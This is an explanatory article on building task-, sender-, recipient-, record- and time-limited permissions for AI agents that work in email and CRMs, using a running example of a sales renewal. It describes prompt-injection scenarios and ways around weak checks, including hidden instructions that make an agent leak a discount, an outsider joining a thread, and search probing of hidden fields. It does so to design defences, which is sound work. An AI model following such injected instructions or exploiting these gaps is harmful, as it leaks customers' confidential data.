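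An app's developer can mark a scope as required, conditionally required or optional. Maya must accept the required scopes to install the app. Conditionally required scopes are compulsory only if the installation link includes them, so a developer can offer different links for different features. HubSpot says users can choose which optional scopes to grant during installation. If the agent's developer made editing optional, Maya could let her agent read deals but not change them.

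However, Maya may not be able to install the agent, because HubSpot only allows this for Super Admins, its most powerful administrators, and users with a permission for marketplace access. Whoever installs it, the scopes can't limit the agent to Acme, since `crm.objects.companies.read` covers companies in general.

### HubSpot apps can see more than their users

In Salesforce, an agent that signs in as Maya has at most Maya's access. An ordinary HubSpot app may have more access than the user who approves it. HubSpot's *Working with OAuth* gives the example of a user who can view only the contacts she owns. If she approves an app's request for `crm.objects.contacts.read`, the app can use the resulting token to view every contact in the company's account.

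A junior salesperson with access to 20 contacts could therefore use the agent to look up any of the company's 20,000, an example of the confused deputy problem. To prevent this, the developer would have to reproduce HubSpot's user permissions in the agent's code.

HubSpot made user-level apps generally available in September 2026, according to *Hubspot Developers Updates & Release Notes* (2026) on Releasebot, a site that collects software announcements. HubSpot checks the signed-in user's own permissions on each request from a user-level app. The developer decides whether an app is user-level, so an administrator evaluating an agent for HubSpot should ask about this before looking at the scopes.

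The same announcements recommend service keys for AI agents and other small integrations. A service key is a credential that someone creates in HubSpot's settings, with a selection of the usual scopes, instead of building a full OAuth app. HubSpot's *Account service keys* shows that automatic rotation is off by default and that the shortest interval available is three months, so a service key is a poor fit for a task that lasts only a few days.

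### What HubSpot's MCP server adds

HubSpot opened its remote MCP server to all customers in April 2026. The server applies the user's own permissions, so the junior salesperson's agent would see only her 20 contacts. This is probably the safest ready-made way to connect Maya's agent to HubSpot.

HubSpot, not the developer, determines the scopes for these connections, based on the tools on the server at the time and the permissions the user grants during installation. Maya has to reinstall the connection to grant new scopes, so at least the agent's access can't grow without her knowledge.

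The tools let an agent do much more than a renewal requires. Besides reading and editing customer records, it can publish web pages and blog posts if the user's permissions and subscription allow it. A hidden instruction could make the agent post Acme's discount on the company's blog without sending an email. Maya should decline any publishing permission that the installation screen makes optional.

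The server can also read emails, calls and meeting notes stored in HubSpot. Many companies keep copies of customer correspondence in the CRM, so Maya's agent could find another customer's emails in HubSpot even if limits on her mailbox stop it from opening them in Microsoft 365.

If a company has turned on HubSpot's Sensitive Data feature, the MCP server blocks emails, calls, meetings, notes and tasks. The ordinary HubSpot interfaces don't apply this block, so an agent connected some other way could still read these records. In October 2026, HubSpot began a public beta in which a Super Admin can let AI connectors read such data. In the beta, the remote MCP server gives read-only access to activities such as emails, but not to sensitive fields.

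In HubSpot, an administrator could come close to limiting an agent to the Acme record by creating a user for the agent, letting it view only records it owns, and making it the owner of Acme's record. The MCP server would then apply that limit. But HubSpot's standard owner field holds only one person, so the agent would normally replace Maya as Acme's owner, which would also affect any reports or reminders that depend on ownership. Salesforce can share a record without changing its owner.

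### The four platforms compared

The table shows who can set each limit on an unattended agent, except where it mentions an add-on. "Developer" means the agent's developer, who chooses what the app requests, and "administrator" means the customer's administrator. The Gmail column covers only OAuth scopes. The Salesforce column includes Named Queries but excludes custom code, which could check almost anything.

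| Limit | Gmail | Microsoft 365 | Salesforce | HubSpot |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Action | Developer | Developer; administrator | Administrator | Developer; user, for optional scopes; administrator |
| Sender | None | Administrator, by copying chosen mail to a separate mailbox | Administrator, for emails stored in the CRM | None |
| Recipient | None | Administrator, with a separate mailbox and mail flow rules | None | None |
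| Record | User, in an add-on: the open message or thread | Administrator: whole mailboxes | Administrator: sharing or a Named Query | Administrator: for example, owned records, through MCP or a user-level app |
| Field | Developer: headers without bodies | Developer: messages without bodies or attachments | Administrator: individual fields | Developer: groups of sensitive fields; administrator: individual fields, through MCP or a user-level app |
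| Validity window | None | Administrator: a timed rule, for sending only | Administrator: refresh token lifetime for the whole app | None; administrators can schedule service key rotation |
| Data window | None | Administrator: new mail only, in a separate mailbox | Administrator: dates in a Named Query | None |
| Task | None | None | None | None |
| Principal's own access | Automatic | Developer: delegated permissions | Automatic | Developer: MCP or a user-level app |

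## How could a permission name senders, recipients and records?

To tell an email to Acme from an email to a competitor, a permission has to depend on the details of each request. One way to write such a permission is as a function:

```
permission(principal, agent, action, arguments, context)
    → allow, deny or ask
```

Here, Maya is the principal. The action might be "send email", with the recipients, text and attachments as its arguments. The context is anything else that affects the decision, such as the date or whether the message the agent is answering really came from Acme. A program outside the model evaluates the function each time the agent requests an operation.

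A scope check is a very simple function of this kind, because it ignores the arguments.

"Ask" holds the operation until Maya approves or refuses it. This suits cases where the facts are uncertain or a refusal might be too strict, such as a reply to someone who has just joined Acme's purchasing team. It works only if Maya is asked rarely. People can't realistically check a long stream of tool calls, as Sharma and colleagues point out, so they switch on automatic approval.

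If Maya has several rules, the program can check them in order, apply the first one that matches, and deny any request that matches none of them. If her company also has rules, the program checks the request against both lists and applies the stricter result.

### Attribute-based access control

Security engineers already have a general model for permissions like this, attribute-based access control (ABAC). The standard description comes from the US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST), where Hu, Ferraiolo and colleagues (2014), in *Guide to Attribute Based Access Control (ABAC) Definition and Considerations*, define it as a method that grants or denies a request by testing attributes against a policy. An attribute is a name with a value, such as "department: cardiology". The policy can use attributes of:

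- the subject, which makes the request
- the object, which the subject wants to use
- the environment, such as the time of day or the current level of threat.

The policy then determines which operations the subject may perform on the object. The subject can be a program, but Hu and colleagues say it must act on behalf of a person or organisation with the authority to perform the operation. For Maya's task, the subject's attributes would therefore describe both the agent and Maya.

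In one example, a hospital lets all nurse practitioners in the cardiology department view the medical records of heart patients. When a new nurse practitioner arrives, the hospital records her job and department, and the existing rule applies to her without anyone having to edit it or list her on each record.

Two older methods are special cases of ABAC. An access control list tests one attribute, the subject's identity, and role-based access control tests another, the subject's role. Both become awkward when a decision depends on several facts. An administrator could create a role called "Maya's agent, Acme renewal, this week", but would need another for every task of every employee. Hu and colleagues call this "role explosion".

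Email doesn't fit the model perfectly, because a recipient is neither the subject making the request nor, in the usual sense, the object. The simplest solution is to treat the outgoing message as the object and its recipients as attributes.

An ABAC decision is only as reliable as the attributes it uses. Hu and colleagues suggest recording how much confidence an attribute deserves, based on who supplied it, how recent it is and how often someone checks it, so that the policy can take that confidence into account. An agent also shouldn't be able to edit the data that its own permissions depend on. Suppose Maya's agent may email any contact on Acme's CRM record and may also edit that record. A hidden instruction could make it add a stranger as a contact and then email him, and every check would return "allow".

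### What does a From address prove?

A rule that lets the agent read only Acme's messages depends on identifying which messages came from Acme. The sender's software writes the From line and can put any address there, so checking that address alone is unreliable. Mail systems use three connected checks to make forgery harder.

With SPF (Sender Policy Framework), a domain's owner publishes a list of the machines that may send its mail. The receiving system checks whether the sending machine is on the list for the domain in the return address given during delivery. That address needn't match the From line. The owner of attacker.example can list his own machine, use attacker.example in the return address, and write `ortiz@acme.example` on the From line. SPF passes because the machine may send mail for attacker.example.

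DKIM (DomainKeys Identified Mail) adds a cryptographic signature that names the domain responsible for a message. An attacker can produce a valid signature by signing with his own domain.

DMARC connects these results to the address that Maya sees. Herr and Levine (2026), in *Domain-Based Message Authentication, Reporting, and Conformance (DMARC)*, set out the current standard, under which the receiving system does the following:

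1. It takes the domain from the From line and looks for a DMARC policy that the domain's owner has published.
2. It runs the SPF and DKIM checks and notes which domains they validated.
3. It passes the message if at least one of those domains matches the domain on the From line.

By default, two domains match if they belong to the same organisation, so a signature from mail.acme.example counts for acme.example. A domain owner can require an exact match, but nearly all find the looser test sufficient. The forged message fails both tests because attacker.example and acme.example belong to different organisations.

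A DMARC pass shows that Acme authorised the use of its domain for this message. It doesn't show that Ortiz wrote the message, because DMARC doesn't check the part of the address before the @ sign. It also doesn't show that the message is harmless. If someone has broken into Ortiz's account, the messages they send from it will pass too.

DMARC also doesn't stop lookalike domains or false display names. An attacker can register acrne.example, with "rn" in place of the "m", and pass every check for that domain. He can also set the display name to "Acme Purchasing" on an unrelated address. Requiring an exact match with a list of Acme's addresses catches both tricks. A sender rule still needs DMARC as well, because a forged From line can contain an address on the list.

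A DMARC failure is weaker evidence than a pass. Herr and Levine warn that some authorised messages fail, and that receiving systems must not reject a message solely because the domain's owner asks them to reject failures. Forged mail may therefore end up in Maya's spam folder, where an agent with access to the whole mailbox can still read it. Some messages have no result because the domain has no DMARC policy or the lookup didn't work. "Ask" is a reasonable answer to both failures and missing results.

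The program that checks the agent's requests doesn't have to repeat this work. Herr and Levine say receiving systems should record the results in a header called `Authentication-Results`. The program should trust only the header that Maya's own mail service added, since a sender can forge one.

### Aliases, mailing lists and forwarded text

Ortiz might write from both `ortiz@acme.example` and `purchasing@acme.example`. A rule based on one address would miss correspondence that uses the other, so her contact record should list every address she uses. Several people may share the purchasing address, in which case the rule admits all of them.

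Mailing lists cause more trouble because they resend messages from their own machines and often alter them, so the messages tend to fail DMARC if the From line is unchanged. List software now avoids this by rewriting the From line. Some lists put their own address there, and others turn an address such as `bob@example.com` into `bob=example.com@user.somelist.example`. If Ortiz asks Maya a question through a trade association's list, a rule for Acme's addresses won't match the message. Maya could add the list's address to the rule, but then anyone who can post to the list could send text to her agent. Developers have spent a decade on ways to leave the From line unchanged, including a protocol called ARC, but Herr and Levine report that none had become widely used by May 2026.

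Simple forwarding is easier to handle. A message that reaches Maya through an old university address will probably fail SPF, because it arrives from the university's server. If Acme signs its mail, the DKIM signature generally remains valid, so the message can still pass DMARC.

All of these checks apply to the sender, who may not have written all the text in the message. Suppose Ortiz forwards an email from one of Acme's suppliers, and the supplier's text contains a hidden instruction. The message comes from a known address and passes DMARC, so the agent reads the instruction. The rule can also hide messages the agent should see. If Maya's colleague forwards her a question from Acme, the agent can't read it because the colleague doesn't work at Acme. A sender rule usefully reduces the number of people who can reach the agent directly, but it doesn't make the text trustworthy.

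### Whom may the agent write to?

Recipients are easier to check than senders in one respect, because the agent has to give the addresses before the message goes out. The difficulty is deciding which ones to allow. There are four common kinds of rule:

| Rule | Whom the agent can write to | Main weakness |
|---|---|---|
| Exact addresses | The people Maya lists | Blocks a legitimate new colleague at Acme |
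| Domain | Anyone at acme.example | Includes people Maya has never dealt with |
| Already in the thread | Everyone on the emails so far | Anyone in the thread can add people |
| Known contact | Anyone in Maya's address book or CRM | Includes her other customers |

The domain rule also fails for small customers who use a public mail service, because allowing their domain would allow millions of strangers. The known-contact rule depends on what counts as a contact. Some mail programs save every address a user writes to, so Maya's address book could include a journalist she once turned down and people who have since moved to competitors.

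Whichever rule Maya chooses must apply to every recipient, including those on the Cc and Bcc lines. An attacker would probably prefer Bcc, because Ortiz can't see who received a blind copy. The service that sends the message has the full list, so the check belongs there or earlier. It should also cover other ways of sending text to an address, such as calendar invitations, which can reveal a customer's discount as easily as an email can.

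A group address doesn't show who will receive the message. Herr and Levine give the example of `finance@association.example`, which relays mail to whoever currently heads finance at an association. Maya may know that person today, but someone else may be behind the same address next month. Her company can look up the members of its own groups before a message goes out, but it can't do this for Acme's. If Maya allows one of Acme's group addresses, she is trusting Acme to manage who belongs to it.

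### How an outsider can defeat the thread rule

"Already in the thread" seems close to what Maya meant by "write to nobody new". It also requires no setup, which makes it attractive to developers. But it lets other people decide whom her agent may write to:

1. On Monday, the thread contains only Maya and Ortiz.
2. On Tuesday, an outsider posing as an adviser to Acme emails Ortiz and asks to be kept informed. Ortiz replies and copies in both the outsider and Maya.
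3. On Wednesday, Ortiz asks Maya about the new price, again copying in everyone.
4. The agent replies to all. Every recipient is already in the thread, so the rule allows the message and the outsider receives the price.

The outsider didn't need to forge an address or hide an instruction, and the agent never had to read anything he wrote. If the agent accepts mail from anyone, the outsider doesn't need Ortiz either, because he can write to Maya himself and copy in an accomplice, which puts him and the accomplice in a thread.

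The solution is to freeze the list of participants when Maya gives her instruction, so that anyone who joins later counts as "new", whoever added them. This is less convenient, because Ortiz may have good reason to bring in a colleague from Acme's legal department. The permission could return "ask" for new people at Acme's domain and "deny" for any other new people.

### Records, fields and labels

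A record rule should use the record's identifier rather than its name. The Salesforce Named Query shown earlier selects accounts called "Acme", so it would also return any other account with that name, including one that a colleague had renamed by mistake.

Listing the fields of a record that the agent may read is safer than listing those it may not. If the company later adds a field for the lowest price it would accept, the agent cannot read that field until someone adds it to the list.

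Neither a sender rule nor a record rule can limit the agent to messages "about its renewal". Ortiz may also write from the same address about an invoice dispute. Maya could label each renewal message and let the agent read only messages with that label. This is more precise, but she would have to label each new message herself or write a filter based on the subject line, which could mislabel some. The agent must not be able to apply the label itself. In Gmail, an agent with `gmail.modify` could add it to any message in her mailbox.

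Attachments need their own conditions. A harmless email from Ortiz may have an attachment that contains a hidden instruction. The agent might also attach a spreadsheet of every customer's price to an otherwise ordinary reply. A rule could ban outgoing attachments or allow only files stored on Acme's record.

Many companies also mark documents and emails with sensitivity labels, such as "Confidential", and write data loss prevention (DLP) rules that restrict what software may do with them. These labels are useful attributes for a permission because they already exist, but they work only if every program checks them everywhere. *Microsoft 365 Copilot Bug Circumvented DLP Controls* (Underhill, 2026) reports that Microsoft's Copilot Chat summarised emails labelled confidential despite such rules. The bug affected the Sent and Drafts folders but not inboxes, according to TechRadar's *Microsoft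 admits an Office bug exposed confidential user emails to Copilot*, which adds that sent threads presumably also include incoming messages. Microsoft told a columnist, whose article appeared on WFMD, that the affected content was emails the user had written. That limits the harm, since people could already read their own mail, but an agent that could also send mail might have passed the text on.

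### Search can reveal what the agent can't open

Hiding a field doesn't always stop people from learning what it contains. If a search runs over hidden data, the list of results can reveal that data.

Horn's *The Hidden Dangers of Salesforce Search and How to Fix Them* describes a company that keeps a "Trade Union Membership" field on its employee records and lets only the personnel department see it. When another employee searches for the phrase, Salesforce hides the field but still returns the matching records, so the employee learns who belongs to a union.

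Salesforce acknowledged in an older edition of its documentation that field-level security doesn't prevent searching on a field's values. According to Horn, its search now enforces the permissions on standard fields and on up to 100 searchable custom fields per object. Beyond that limit, search can still match on values the user can't see. Since summer 2024, administrators have been able to choose which custom fields are protected. They can also remove a field from the search index, which stops anyone from finding records by its contents.

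An agent makes this kind of leak easier to exploit because it can run hundreds of searches that a person would find tedious. Suppose a hidden field on Acme's record contains the note "will accept 15% discount". A malicious instruction could make the agent search for "accept 5%", "accept 10%" and so on until Acme's record appears.

In Salesforce's Apex language, a search by default does not enforce the user's field permissions and can match on every searchable field, so one broad search in an otherwise careful custom tool for Maya's agent could reintroduce the leak. The developer should limit the search to particular types of field and check the user's permissions explicitly.

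Salesforce applies its permissions on records after the search has run, which can also produce incomplete answers. In Horn's example, 2,800 records match a query. Salesforce examines the first 2,000, removes 400 that the user isn't allowed to see, and shows the other 1,600. It never examines the remaining 800, although the user may have access to some of them. An agent using this search could wrongly tell a customer that the company has no record of a request.

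Other companies handle the problem differently:

- IBM's *Field level security* tells administrators to leave restricted fields out of global search, because users might work out the hidden values.
- ServiceNow's *Security for searchable referenced table field values in AI Search* says that, for fields indexed from linked tables, results include only values the user may view. Values whose access depends on a condition or script don't appear at all.
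- Gmail refuses searches from apps that have only the `gmail.metadata` scope, according to Google's *Method*, its reference for listing messages. Google doesn't give a reason there, but the effect is that an app without access to message bodies can't find out what they contain by searching for words.

The safest arrangement for Maya's agent is to apply the permission first and then search only the data it allows. If the agent may read four fields of one record, its searches should cover only those four fields.

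### Do finer permissions multiply without end?

Sharma and colleagues argue that finer scopes can't solve the problem, because the number of scopes grows too quickly. If Maya has 200 contacts, there are 2^200 possible sets of recipients, or about 1.6 × 10^60, since each contact is either in a set or not. No platform could offer a named scope for each set.

This calculation slightly overstates the problem with named scopes. A token can carry several scopes, so a platform could offer one per contact, and any set of contacts could be described by combining some of those 200 scopes. That number is manageable, although the consent screen would be very hard to use.

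The number of scopes grows much faster when one condition depends on another. Suppose Maya lets her agent attach a customer's quote to an email only if the email is going to that customer. If she grants separate scopes for contacts and quotes, the agent can send Acme's quote to another customer. To prevent this, the platform would need a scope for each pair of contact and quote. With 200 contacts and one quote for each of her 60 customers, that is 12,000 scopes for a single action. Chen and colleagues describe a similar "scope explosion" in a home with hundreds of connected devices, where the owner might have to review thousands of permissions.

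A predicate avoids this. It is a condition that is either true or false for each request, such as:

```
every recipient is a contact of the customer
whose quote is attached
```

This one condition replaces all 12,000 scopes, and it still works when Maya gains a 61st customer. A predicate can also test a quantity directly, such as whether a payment is at most $500. To offer amounts as scopes, a payment service would have to divide them into ranges.

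A predicate can also describe any of the 2^200 sets. If the set follows no pattern, the predicate has to list its members, which takes at most 200 names. But people usually choose recipients for a reason, and a description like "Acme's contacts" is much shorter than the list.

So the argument about numbers applies to named scopes but not to finer permissions in general. Separately, Sharma and colleagues object that a list of allowed values can't anticipate values that the agent computes during a task.

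With a predicate, unlike a named scope, Maya can't always tell what she is agreeing to, because what it matches depends on data that may change. "Acme's contacts" might include someone who left Acme last year, or whoever a colleague adds tomorrow. A consent screen could reduce the problem by showing her the names that currently match.

Gmail can already check some of the conditions Maya needs. Google's *Searching for Messages* explains that an app can filter messages by sender, date or label, for example to find all the mail a user sent in January 2014. But the app writes the query and can leave the filter out. To turn the filter into a permission, Google would have to store it with Maya's grant and apply it to every request.

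### The conditions for Maya's task

Apart from its deadline, Maya's instruction could become the following rules. A program would read each group from top to bottom and stop at the first rule that matches.

```
ACME_PEOPLE    = the Acme addresses Maya had corresponded with
                 when she gave the instruction
RENEWAL_FIELDS = name, renewal date, renewal price, contract length

Read a message
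  allow  if the From address is in ACME_PEOPLE and DMARC passed
  ask    if the From address is in ACME_PEOPLE

Read or search records
  allow  if the only record is Acme's
         and every field is in RENEWAL_FIELDS

Send a message
  deny   if it has an attachment
  allow  if every To, Cc and Bcc address is in ACME_PEOPLE
  ask    if every To, Cc and Bcc address is at acme.example

Anything else
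  deny
```

Here is how the rules would treat four requests from the agent:

| Request | Answer | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| Read an email from `ortiz@acme.example` that failed DMARC | Ask | The address is known, but the message may be forged |
| Search all customers' records for "18% discount" | Deny | The search covers more than Acme's record |
| Reply to Ortiz, with a copy to the outside adviser | Deny | The adviser isn't at acme.example |
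| Reply to Ortiz alone, giving the renewal price | Allow | Ortiz was a contact when the task began |

The first request could involve the forged email with the hidden instruction to forward last month's messages. If Maya refuses the request, the email never reaches the model. If she approves it by mistake, the rule for sending still blocks any message to the outside address.

After the third refusal, the agent can remove the adviser from the recipients and send the same reply to Ortiz. Ortiz may then forward it to the adviser, and no permission at Maya's company can prevent that.

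The fourth reply could still contain something Acme shouldn't see, since no rule applies to its text. But the agent couldn't have read another customer's discount in the CRM, so it has less to reveal. The rules also let the agent read and answer Ortiz's emails about the invoice dispute. Maya could exclude those by requiring her renewal label on every message the agent reads, but she would have to keep labelling messages until Friday.

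## How could a permission be limited by time, use and task?

Maya's deadline limits when her agent may work, but not how far back it may read. A token that expires in an hour can still give access to ten years of mail. At ten messages a second, an agent could copy 36,000 messages in that hour.

A permission therefore needs two separate periods. The validity window is when the credential works, and the data window is the range of dates from which the agent may read data. Maya's instruction sets a validity window, from now until Friday at 17:00, but no data window. If the renewal talks began on 1 September, she could let the agent read only mail received since then, so that it couldn't read last year's argument about late payments.

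The program that checks the data window should use the time Maya's mail service received each message, because a sender can forge the date in the header as easily as the From line. New messages can also contain old text. If Ortiz replies to a thread from 2023, the agent may read her reply and everything quoted below it.

### Start and expiry times

Many tokens include dates, stored in signed statements called claims. The `exp` claim gives the time the token expires, `iat` gives the time the server issued it, and `nbf` ("not before") can delay its start. In an example from *Global Token Revocation* (Parecki, 2026), `iat` is 1741200000 and `exp` is 1741200300, both in seconds, so the token works for five minutes.

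The count starts from the same moment everywhere in the world, so it means the same time in every time zone once someone has converted "Friday at 17:00" correctly. If Maya is in London and the software assumes New York time, her agent gets five extra hours.

An agent with a refresh token can get a new access token when a short-lived one expires, so the authorisation server would have to store Maya's 17:00 deadline with the grant and refuse to renew after it. The server would also have to make the last token expire by the deadline. If the agent renews at 16:50 and receives the usual one-hour token, it can work until 17:50, so the server should issue a ten-minute token instead.

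Some permissions should work only at certain times of the week. Chen and colleagues give the example of Bob, who allows his home hub to turn on the bedroom lights, set the thermostat and start the coffee maker at 07:00 on weekdays. A refresh token lets the hub keep doing this without asking him again, but OAuth has no standard way to limit the permission to those times. Developers have to build the limit into the hub or the devices. If only the hub enforces it, a faulty hub can ignore it.

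An authorisation server could get much the same effect by issuing the hub a ten-minute token at 07:00 each weekday and none at other times. Maya could also use a recurring window, such as 09:00 to 17:00 on working days, so that she is at her desk when the agent needs her approval.

### What happens to a message sent after the deadline?

At 16:55 on Friday, the agent writes a reply to Ortiz and schedules it for Monday at 09:00. If the mail service checks the permission only when the agent submits the message, it accepts the reply and sends it 64 hours after Maya's deadline.

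The mail service could check again when it sends the message. *Runtime Authorization for Resources Acquired by AI Agents* (Zhu and Wang, 2026) proposes this kind of check for agents' actions in general. Its system issues a permit for a single action, then rechecks the permit, including its expiry time, in the same step that carries out the action. If one program checked the permit and then called another that acted without checking, the deadline could pass or Maya could cancel the task in between, and the action would still go ahead.

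A strict check would also stop a reply that the agent submitted at 16:59 but a busy server held for two minutes. Maya would probably want that reply sent. The mail service could allow a few minutes for ordinary delays but refuse any message scheduled for after the deadline. If she cancels the task, the service should hold everything still in the queue, though it can't recall a message that Acme's server has already accepted.

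### Limits on number, rate and amount

Maya might also want to limit how much the agent does before Friday. Chen and colleagues describe a research assistant that downloads hundreds of papers through its user's subscription. The database service wrongly flags this as an attack and locks the account, so the user loses access too. A limit of 100 papers an hour could prevent this, but an ordinary scope can't express it.

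If a limit of 100 downloads an hour resets on the hour, the agent can download 100 papers at 09:59 and another 100 at 10:00. The system can prevent this by counting the downloads from the previous 60 minutes at each request. A limit of 20 emails also offers little protection if each one can go to 500 people, and a cap of $500 per payment still allows ten payments that total $5,000.

The count of remaining uses has to be stored on the server. If the token contained the words "20 emails left", the agent could present the same token with every email and the number would never fall. If several servers handle the agent's requests, they must share the count.

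Suppose Maya allows 20 emails and the agent has sent 19. It submits two replies at the same moment, and a different server handles each:

| Step | Server A | Server B | Stored count |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Reads the count: 19 | Reads the count: 19 | 19 |
| 2 | Sends the reply to Ortiz | Sends the reply to her colleague | 19 |
| 3 | Writes 20 | Writes 20 | 20 |

The agent has now sent 21 emails, and the stored count is wrong. To prevent this, the database should check the count and increase it in one indivisible step before either email goes out. The server whose update runs first can send the last permitted email, and the other refuses its request.

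Suppose Server A sends the reply to Ortiz, using the last of the agent's 20 permitted sends, but the connection fails before the agent receives confirmation. When the agent tries again, the server refuses because the limit has been reached, and the agent wrongly tells Maya that the reply was never sent. If the limit had been 30, Ortiz would have received the email twice and the agent would have used two sends.

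The usual solution is an idempotency key, an identifier that the agent attaches to the request and reuses when it retries. If the server has already processed a request with that key, it returns the original confirmation without sending or counting the email again. It should refuse a retry that has the same key but a different recipient or text. Biometric Update's *A verified user doesn’t give an AI agent unlimited authority* describes the same approach for an assistant that requests access to a company dashboard. If the response times out, an identical retry returns the original tracking number instead of creating another request.

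If Server A itself cannot determine whether the email went out, it should keep the place reserved until it can. Zhu and Wang likewise treat a timeout as an unknown result rather than a failure.

A budget is harder to enforce when the agents spending it use services run by different companies. In another of Chen and colleagues' examples, a user allows 100 units for a business trip, and her assistant has one agent book the flight and another book the hotel. If each agent spends 60, each booking is within the limit but the trip costs 120. OAuth has no standard way for the two services to consult the same running total. The user could give each agent 50, but then a flight costing 60 would fail even if the hotel cost only 30.

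### The task as a limit

Maya wants the agent's access to end when the renewal is done, and limits on time and number of uses only approximate that. If Acme signs on Wednesday, the agent has no reason to keep reading her mail until Friday.

To enforce this, the company's software needs a record of the task with an identifier such as `acme-renewal-17`. The record shows who gave the instruction, which limits apply and whether the task is still open. Every token and request includes the identifier, and the server checks the record before allowing a request. The task could end when Maya cancels it or when the CRM shows that Acme has signed. The task still needs a deadline, because Acme may never sign and Maya may forget to cancel.

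The agent can safely report that it has finished, since that only reduces its access. It shouldn't be able to reopen the task, move the deadline or edit the CRM field that shows whether Acme has signed.

A task identifier also lets a permission cover things that nobody could name in advance. When Maya gives her instruction on Monday, she can't list the draft reply that the agent will write on Tuesday. But she can let the agent edit any draft it creates during this task, as long as the server stores the task's identifier with each one. Google Drive's `drive.file` scope similarly covers files that an app creates, but it isn't tied to a task, so an agent could still open the files it made for Maya's previous customer.

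Rich Authorization Requests, an extension to OAuth, lets an agent ask for permission to pay a particular amount to a particular recipient. But Chen and colleagues point out that an agent planning a picnic doesn't know the cost until it has chosen a park. They suggest letting the user approve limits instead, such as $100 for supplies within ten miles. The authorisation server would check each later request against those limits.

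### What if the agent acquires new access?

Some things an agent creates can extend its access. For example, Maya's agent might open a free file-sharing account to send Acme a large document. The account has its own password, so it keeps working after Friday even if every token for Maya's mail and CRM has expired.

Zhu and Wang designed their system for this problem. In one of their examples, an agent is allowed to spend $20 on one isolated, read-only cloud computer for a task. The agent orders the right product at the right price, but the computer the provider delivers comes with an administrator's credential and access to outside networks. The purchase still passes every check, because the checks don't cover what the provider returned.

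Their solution is a broker, a program between the agent and the provider, which works as follows:

1. The broker checks the proposed purchase, reserves the money and places the order.
2. It quarantines whatever the provider returns, so the agent can't use it yet.
3. It finds out from the provider what the new resource can do. If some detail is missing, it assumes the broadest access that the detail could allow, or refuses if it can't set such a bound.
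4. It checks the resource against the task's limits, together with everything the agent has already acquired.
5. If the resource passes, the broker gives the agent a reference to it but keeps the credential. Each use then needs a single-use permit of the kind described above.

The fourth step catches combinations that look harmless separately. A policy might let an agent hold either a credential for reading sensitive data or one for publishing outside the company, but not both. An agent could also open four free accounts under different names when the task allows one, and a budget wouldn't stop it. After a refund, the agent may still have a working credential, so the broker keeps counting the resource until it has proof that nobody can use it any more.

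Each permit also records the version of the policy under which the broker issued it. An administrator can cancel all the permits issued under one version simply by changing to a new version.

Zhu and Wang tested the design on 60 cases covering services, usage quotas, computers, credentials and other agents. It accepted all 20 harmless cases and rejected all 40 unsafe ones. Six simpler checks, including one that covered only price and one that covered only OAuth scopes, accepted all 60. Zhu and Wang built the cases to pass those simpler checks, so the comparison can't show how often real systems would fail.

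In a smaller test, they connected parts of two real agent programs to Docker, which runs software in isolated containers. Both harmless cases finished, and none of the 16 unsafe ones led to an unauthorised request to start a container. In the main test, the broker's own processing took a median of about two milliseconds per case, excluding network and storage delays.

No language model chose the actions in these tests, and no outside provider took part. The safety proofs also assume that every acquisition goes through the broker. If Maya's agent has an ordinary web browser, it could open the file-sharing account without going through the broker.

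### Can OAuth cancel a task?

Chen and colleagues want a user to be able to say "Cancel the picnic planning" and end all the permissions and pending actions for that task, without disturbing the agent's other work. They find that OAuth has no standard command for this, such as one to revoke everything connected with "picnic-task-123". An application would have to keep its own list of which tokens belong to which task. They also identify several related gaps:

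| What a user or company may want | What OAuth offers | What is missing |
|---|---|---|
| Permission only at certain times or up to a certain rate | Named scopes | A standard way to state and enforce the condition |
| One budget for several agents | Separate grants | A total that different organisations' services can share |
| A new agent joining partway through a task | A new grant for that agent | A way to add it to the existing task and end all the agents' access together |
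| Proof that the user approved a particular payment | A token showing that the agent may make payments | A signed record of the approval, with the amount and recipient |
| An immediate end to all access after a break-in | Revocation of one token at a time | A standard way to revoke everything for a user or an app |

A revised draft dated 25 August 2026 adds a gap that Chen and colleagues call silent execution. If an action falls within an existing grant, the agent can carry it out without showing the user a consent screen or getting anyone's approval for that action, even if it is irreversible. The analysis relies on hypothetical scenarios, so it can't show how often any of these gaps causes harm. A company can fill many of them with its own software, though other companies' services may not support it.

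Lodderstedt, Dronia and Scurtescu (2013), in *OAuth 2.0 Token Revocation*, define a request that names one token to cancel. When that token is a refresh token, the server should also cancel the access tokens from the same grant, if it supports doing so. Chen and colleagues' claim that the standard revokes a single token is therefore slightly too strong. An agent could obtain a separate grant for each task, and cancelling one refresh token would then end that task's access on one platform. This works only if each platform keeps the grants for different tasks separate. Maya would also have to go through the consent screen again for every task, and the agent would need to cancel its mail and CRM grants separately.

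The request also has to come from the application that received the token. Maya can't send it herself, so she has to trust the agent's developer to send it at the right time. Lodderstedt and colleagues allow for other ways for users to revoke grants, usually through an account page, but these pages tend to list apps rather than tasks.

Even a successful request to cancel a token may not end access immediately. Some access tokens contain everything the resource server needs to check them, so it doesn't consult the authorisation server and may keep accepting a cancelled token. At Resend, an email service for developers, cancelling a refresh token stops every token from the same grant, according to its *Revoke Token* documentation. At the printing service ezeep, access tokens can last up to an hour after the refresh token is cancelled, according to ezeep's *Token Revocation*.

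Parecki proposes a command that cancels all of a user's refresh tokens. This would help after a break-in, but it's too broad for ending one task, because it could also disconnect Maya's calendar and phone. The server should cancel her access tokens too, but doesn't have to. The server's success response means only that cancellation has begun.

### Short expiry or revocation signals?

With short-lived tokens, nobody has to send a cancellation to the mail service or CRM. If Maya cancels the task and the authorisation server stops renewing the agent's tokens, the agent loses access when its current token expires. With one-hour tokens, that takes up to an hour, or 30 minutes on average if she cancels at a random moment. Five-minute tokens cut the average to two and a half minutes, but the agent must renew each one 12 times an hour. If the authorisation server is down for more than five minutes,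 every agent that depends on it stops working.

A revocation signal can end access sooner. *OpenID Continuous Access Evaluation Profile 1.0* (Cappalli and Tulshibagwale, 2025) defines messages that one system can send another to reduce someone's access during a session. A companion standard, the Shared Signals Framework, delivers the messages and lets the two systems agree on which events and users they cover (Tulshibagwale, 2025, *SGNL welcomes the publication of the final Shared Signals and CAEP specifications!*). If Maya's company ended her session, its sign-in service could notify the mail service without waiting for a token to expire.

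The OpenID Foundation's *CAEP Interoperability Profile* (2026) doesn't yet give Maya a ready-made way to cancel a task. Its use cases cover revoked sessions, changed credentials and changes in whether a device meets the company's rules. A company could open a separate session for each task and revoke it when the task ends, but the mail service and the CRM would both have to support this.

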